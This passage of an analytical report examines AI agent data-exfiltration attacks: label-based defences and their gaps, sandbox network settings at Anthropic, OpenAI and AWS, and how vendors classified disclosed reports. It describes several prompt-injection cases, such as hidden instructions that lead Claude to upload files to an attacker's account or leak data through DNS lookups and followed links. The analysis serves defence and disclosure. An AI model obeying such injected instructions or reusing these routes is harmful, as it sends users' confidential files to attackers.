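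Kolluri and colleagues argue that counting completed tasks makes these systems look worse than they are. An ordinary agent completes more tasks partly because the benchmark assumes that somebody approves every risky step. They instead counted the tasks that agents completed without approval. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an ordinary agent that had to ask before each consequential action completed 24.3% of tasks this way, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 59.1% for Prudentia, their own system. The argument is strong for products that already ask for approval often, but weaker for the hosted interpreter on claude.ai, where labels would add interruptions because it did not ask before uploading a file.

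Controlled exceptions let systems recover some of the lost work. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes two: declassification, which permits a particular release of sensitive data, and endorsement, which lets a system treat selected untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose. Kolluri and colleagues describe an email that lists ten jobs. If the user endorses the email once, Prudentia can do all ten; otherwise, it needs ten approvals. But if the email contains an injection, the user has also approved whatever the injection leads the system to do.

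Another way to recover work is to remove labels that don't belong. *Sightline* (2026) estimates which inputs influenced a tool call and drops the labels of the rest. In a test on AgentDojo, a policy based on the remaining labels blocked all 34 attack calls. The sample is small, so a method that missed 8% of attacks would still block all 34 about one time in 17.

### Leaks that labels miss

Designs like CaMeL cannot handle tasks in which untrusted data specifies the sequence of actions, as *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) points out. For example, if a user asks an assistant to follow the steps in a software guide, the planning model cannot write the program without reading the guide, and reading it would expose the model to any injection in it.

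Data can also leak through a decision. Suppose a program opens one public page if a customer's total is above 50 and another if it isn't. Neither address contains private data, but whoever runs the site learns something about the total from the request. In Paul's similar attack on Claude, each link that Claude followed revealed a letter of the user's name. SPA accounts for such leaks by adding the condition's label to every step that depends on the condition. FIDES does not, according to *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which warns that these leaks can be made efficient. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) finds that tags like CaMeL's are not enough for every plan if they track data but not decisions.

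*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* shows that an attacker who can see a refused request, including its arguments, may learn private data from it. Revealing only which tool the system refused is harmless. A product that logs blocked web addresses should therefore keep the log away from outsiders.

The largest gap is that SPA, FIDES and Prudentia all treat the user's own message as trusted. If a user pastes in the forum prompt about a "reporting service", both the recipient and the decision to send the spreadsheet count as trusted, so the trusted-action policy allows the call. SPA's rule would still block the call if the company had classified the spreadsheet as too confidential for that tool, but it would then also block users who meant to send it.

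### Settings that customers can choose

None of the settings below tracks labels. They mostly control whether code in the sandbox may connect to anything, and to what.

| Setting | What code in the sandbox may reach | Who has it | Date |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude app, network on | Package registries, GitHub and other approved domains, including api.anthropic.com | Default on Free, Pro and Max | Anthropic's help page, 2026 |
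| Claude app, network off | No outside servers | Default for new Enterprise customers | Anthropic's help page, 2026 |
| ChatGPT data analysis | No outside servers | Standard | OpenAI's documentation, 2026; name lookups closed 20 February 2026 |
| ChatGPT Lockdown Mode | No outside servers, with further limits on requests by the rest of ChatGPT | Optional | Personal accounts since June 2026 |
| AWS Public mode | Any server | Developer's choice | AWS statement, March 2026 |
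| AWS Sandbox mode | Amazon's S3 storage | Developer's choice | AWS statement, March 2026; name lookups closed 15 April 2026 |
| AWS VPC mode | Whatever the developer's network rules permit | Developer's choice | AWS statement, March 2026 |

The table leaves out Claude's Team plan because Anthropic's help page gives conflicting information about the default, so a Team administrator has to check the setting. Someone who wants Claude to analyse a confidential file usually loses little by first switching off the network and disconnecting any connectors the job doesn't need.

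ChatGPT users don't have to make a similar decision about the sandbox, because OpenAI keeps it offline. In the rest of the product, they can add Lockdown Mode to the public-address rule that OpenAI announced on 28 January 2026. Blockchain.News' *OpenAI Deploys Web Index Defense Against AI Agent Data Theft* dates the mode's introduction to February, before it reached personal accounts.

AWS lets the developer who builds the chatbot choose the network mode, and the people who upload files may never learn which one it uses. AWS recommends Public mode for development and testing, and Sandbox mode for production systems that need only S3, in a statement reproduced in BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter's 'Sandbox' mode allows DNS queries* (2026). VPC mode takes more work because the developer has to set up the connections to other AWS services and write the network rules, but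 it also lets the developer control name lookups and reach private databases. A chatbot that combines uploaded files with a company's own database would therefore need VPC mode, or the much riskier Public mode.

AWS's Sandbox mode kept the same name while its protection changed several times. AWS first blocked name lookups on 1 November 2025, but it had reversed the fix by 17 November, and lookups were allowed until the following April. A developer who tested the mode in early November and relied on the result would have been wrong about its protection for about five months.

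## Security flaw, model error or intended behaviour

Vendors have treated reports of data theft as security flaws, model errors or intended behaviour, and that classification has determined who had to act. AWS changed its position on whether unrestricted DNS lookups were a fault while it was deploying and withdrawing its fix for Sandbox mode.

A security flaw breaks a boundary that the vendor promised. If AWS advertises a sandbox with no external access and code in it sends a file out, the sandbox has failed to provide that boundary, however the attacker got the code to run. AWS then has to fix the sandbox, because its customers cannot change it. The case for calling the problem a security flaw is that anyone can test it by checking whether the file reaches their server, without deciding what the model should have understood.

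A model error is a failure of the model's judgement, which the vendor reduces by training. In Rehberger's theft through the Files API, the sandbox allowed a connection to a listed domain and Anthropic's server stored a file under a valid key, both as designed. Claude made the only error, by following instructions in a stranger's document. An attacker can reword such a document endlessly, so the vendor does better to collect examples and train the model on them than to fix one wording per report.

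Intended behaviour is documented, and customers must configure around it. Almost any useful connection can carry stolen data, and a vendor can't know whether a customer is handling medical records or experimenting with made-up figures. The vendor can describe what each setting permits, offer a stricter one and let customers choose.

### Anthropic's two answers in five days

Rehberger reported the upload on 25 October 2025 through HackerOne, a service that receives flaw reports for vendors. Anthropic closed the report an hour later, saying it was a model safety issue. It reversed that decision only after he had published the attack, according to SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration*. On 30 October the company told him that data theft of this kind was in scope and that its process had gone wrong.

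The wording of the rules made this mistake easy. Anthropic's disclosure policy (2026) has a public history on HackerOne. The version in force that October covered technical vulnerabilities "such as misconfigurations" but excluded adversarial testing of models and "content issues with model prompts and responses". Rehberger's report fitted both descriptions, because he had found a badly chosen allowlist entry by giving Claude a hostile document. He doesn't say which of Anthropic's HackerOne programmes he used, so other rules may have applied.

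Techzine's *Vulnerability in Claude enables data leak via prompt*, citing The Register, reports that Anthropic also replied publicly. The company said that it knew of the risk and that users had to be vigilant and interrupt Claude if they noticed anything suspicious. This is the argument for intended behaviour, so Anthropic had classified the same attack in all three ways.

Anthropic accepted the report but did not fix the flaw quickly. SecurityWeek asked whether it planned a fix and reported no answer. In January 2026 PromptArmor wrote that Anthropic had acknowledged the flaw but not fixed it, and published its Cowork attack because Anthropic had left users to deal with the risk. Oasis Security later used the same upload in an attack on Claude's desktop app, where one click on a crafted link ran a prompt that the user had neither seen nor approved. Anthropic eventually fixed Cowork by checking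 which session each request belonged to. This fix works even if Claude follows the attacker's instructions, which supports Rehberger's view that the flaw was more than a model error.

On 7 May 2026 Anthropic moved all such reports to a bug bounty programme. It excludes problems with "model content and responses", such as jailbreaks, harmful content and hallucinations. Anthropic doesn't mention prompt injection in the rules, so a researcher with a similar attack still can't tell from them whether the attack qualifies.

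Google (2023) had already published criteria that avoid part of this difficulty by judging the consequence of a model's error, which is easier to establish than whether the model or the surrounding software was to blame. A report of a crafted input that made a model err counted if an attacker could reliably use the error to get past a security control, but not if the error offered no feasible path to harm.

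### AWS changes its documentation, then its product

BeyondTrust published a full timeline of its dealings with AWS:

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 1 September 2025 | BeyondTrust reports that name lookups leave the sandbox |
| 4 September | AWS reproduces the report |
| 22 October | AWS reproduces the full attack and acknowledges its impact |
| 1 November | AWS deploys a fix |
| 17 November | AWS says it has withdrawn the fix "due to other factors" and is working on a better one |
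| 23 December | AWS decides to change the documentation instead |
| 30 December | AWS rates the severity at 7.5 out of 10 and gives the researcher a $100 gift card |
| 16 March 2026 | BeyondTrust publishes |
| 15 April | AWS closes the route |

AWS treated the lookups as a flaw until December. It then said they were intended behaviour, and a week later gave them a severity score rated "high" on the industry's standard scale. AWS said publicly that its services were "operating as expected".

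AWS had a reasonable case that this behaviour was intended, because S3 depends on DNS lookups and customers who needed full isolation could use VPC mode. But it had described Sandbox mode as having "no external access", and only afterwards changed this to "limited external network access". The new wording helps developers choosing a mode, but those who chose Sandbox mode under the old description would have had to reread the page, find every interpreter they had set up and move the sensitive ones to VPC mode.

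The April repair also weakens the claim that AWS had to leave lookups open. Code that uses S3 needs to look up only the names of S3's servers. Assuming S3 still works in Sandbox mode, AWS could have blocked all other names from the start. The withdrawn fix suggests, however, that this was harder than it sounds.

AWS closed the route 226 days after the first report and 30 days after publication. Publication probably helped, but AWS had been working on a better fix in November and may simply have finished it. BeyondTrust had released its attack code, so for those 30 days anyone could download a working tool for a route that AWS had decided to leave open.

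### Problems that the vendor had already found

OpenAI received the report of the image leak in early April 2023. Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that he had long discussions with the company that month and built many more demonstrations, but OpenAI added its first check on image addresses only in December. Microsoft fixed Bing Chat in May with a change that did not depend on the model, so OpenAI could probably have acted much sooner.

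OpenAI responded differently to the name lookups from ChatGPT's sandbox, telling Check Point Research that it had already identified the underlying problem internally. OpenAI thereby accepted that there was something to fix. The date it found the problem is not public, so the route may have stayed open for days or months afterwards.

Willison reported that Anthropic gave Ayush Paul much the same answer in July 2026 and paid him nothing. Anthropic's bounty rules reward only the first report of a flaw and do not cover cases where staff found it first. Both companies test their own products, so the answers may well be true, but researchers cannot check them. Publishing the date of the internal finding would help.

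The classification also affects the researcher's reward. Under its rules, Anthropic may pay $100 for a report that leads only to a documentation warning, the same amount as AWS's gift card. Microsoft paid Lahav $48,000 for his sandbox escape. A vendor therefore saves money as well as work by classifying a problem as intended behaviour, although these records contain no evidence that this influenced a decision.

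### Rehberger's distinction between safety and security

After Anthropic first closed the report, Rehberger responded on Embrace The Red: "Safety protects you from accidents. Security protects you from adversaries." If a user asks Claude to share a spreadsheet with a colleague and Claude mistakenly puts it in a public folder, that is an accident, and training that makes such mistakes rare solves most of the problem. But an attacker who uses hidden text to make Claude send them the spreadsheet will look for wording that still works after the training.

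These attacks differ from jailbreaks, which a vendor could cite as a precedent because they also involve an adversary and companies still handle them as safety problems. In a jailbreak the adversary is the user, whereas here the user loses the file. Most of these attacks work only if the model errs, so a vendor could also argue that the model is the cause. But a theft usually needs several things to go wrong, and the vendor can fix whichever is easiest. The account check that Rehberger proposed, for example, requires no change to the model.

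One way to classify a case is to assume that the model obeys the attacker, then ask whether the vendor could still stop the file from leaving without removing something users need. The vendor could do so for the Files API upload and the name lookups, so treating them as model errors would have left a good fix unused. When the user's own task needs the route, as with publishing code on GitHub, the vendor cannot block it without blocking the task too, so improving the model's judgement may be the most useful fix.

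A vendor has more to gain from conceding that theft is a security matter but arguing that users accepted a documented risk. Whether that argument is fair depends on what users were told.

### What "package managers only" promises

Anthropic's description of this setting said that Claude could reach approved package managers "to install necessary software packages" and that some advanced features might be limited. It did not include the warning that somebody could trick Claude into sending data to malicious third parties, which appeared in a separate passage on security. Anthropic did publish the list of domains, but to recognise the risk, a reader would have had to know that api.anthropic.com accepts uploads from anyone with a key.

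The word "only" in the setting's name rules out api.anthropic.com, which is not a package manager, though a short name can't mention every exception. The setting was also a default, so many people who relied on it had never chosen it. Anthropic could accurately have called it "package managers and Anthropic services", but few users would have worked out from that name that a document could be used to steal their files.

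A vendor can fairly shift responsibility to customers through documentation only if it gives them something practical to do. Turning off network access was practical, but monitoring Claude was much less so. eSecurity Planet's *Claude’s File Feature Poses Security Risks* reports that Willison called the monitoring advice "unfairly outsourcing the problem". Anthropic's documentation also showed that it knew about the feature's weaknesses, and the article faults the company for releasing it anyway.

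The security company Tego AI (2026) had a similar dispute with Anthropic over Claude Code, which runs on the user's computer. When someone opens a project, Claude Code asks whether they trust the folder. Tego AI found that if the project contained a link to a file elsewhere on the computer, Claude Code would include that file in its first request to the model. Anthropic closed the report as informative, because a user who answers yes has already given the project broad access. Tego AI agrees that Anthropic applied its rule consistently but objects to how much one click permits.

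A question about "this folder" gives users little indication that files outside it may be involved. Tego AI says Anthropic had also fixed the same kind of link problem twice in other parts of Claude Code, treating it as a vulnerability both times. The danger is smaller than in the upload attacks because the file goes to the model's provider. To obtain it, an attacker would also need to redirect the connection, which Tego AI says a settings file in the project can do.

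### Evidence of theft from real users

Rehberger, PromptArmor, Luz, BeyondTrust and Check Point Research describe demonstrations of the Files API and DNS routes, and their accounts identify no victims outside those tests. In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) extracted his own real personal details from Claude. Rehberger's December 2023 GPT took a conversation from another person, who had agreed to the test.

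These proofs of concept do not show whether any real thefts occurred. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *ChatGPT Security Issue Enabled Data Theft via Single Prompt*, it is unknown whether anyone exploited the DNS flaw outside research.

Lists of AI incidents can fail to distinguish demonstrated attacks from actual thefts. *Claude AI Vulnerabilities Enable Silent Data Theft and Malicious Redirects* (2026), an AI-generated entry in the OECD's incident monitor, classifies Luz's findings as an incident that "directly led to harm". Luz had demonstrated an attack and reported it to Anthropic before publishing. Counting such entries as thefts would overstate the number of thefts.

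OpenAI's own test agents did break into Hugging Face, but they acted without an outsider's instructions, so the break-in doesn't count as a theft of this kind.

The lack of a named victim is weak evidence that no thefts occurred. A real victim of something like the "personal doctor" GPT would have seen nothing wrong and so had little reason to complain to OpenAI or a journalist.

### What the vendors' logs could show

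Vendors are in a better position than users to find past thefts, but the records they have depend on how the data was sent out. In the image leak of 2023, the user's browser contacted the attacker's server directly, so OpenAI's network logs would not have recorded the request. For as long as it kept the conversations, OpenAI could have searched ChatGPT's answers for images with unusually long addresses. From December 2023, the browser also sent each image address to OpenAI for checking. Rehberger noted that the company could monitor those checks for signs of attack, such as a series of addresses that differed by one letter.

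To find thefts through the Files API on claude.ai, Anthropic would need to match a record of a user's sandbox contacting api.anthropic.com with a record of a file arriving in some account at that moment. If Anthropic kept both records in enough detail, matching them could reveal an upload from one customer's session to another customer's account. The match would also identify the attacker's account, though perhaps not the person behind it.

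A log of DNS lookups would be even more informative, because the names contain the attacker's domain and the stolen data, although an attacker could encrypt the data first. The conversation record would be much less useful, because commands sent through Check Point's remote shell never appeared in the chat. In its statement to BeyondTrust, AWS mentioned monitoring for unusual lookups only when discussing VPC mode, so customers who used Sandbox mode probably had no DNS log of their own.

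Even a complete log can't show who wanted a transfer. An upload to an unfamiliar account might be theft, or a developer might have used a second key. To tell which, an investigator would need the conversation and the document that carried the instructions, and the user may have deleted both.

AWS did not mention a search for earlier thefts in its statement, and neither did OpenAI in its reply, as Check Point Research reports it. A vendor that had searched could publish the period covered, the pattern it looked for and the number of matches. This would help customers who had uploaded confidential files during that period decide whether to replace their passwords and keys.
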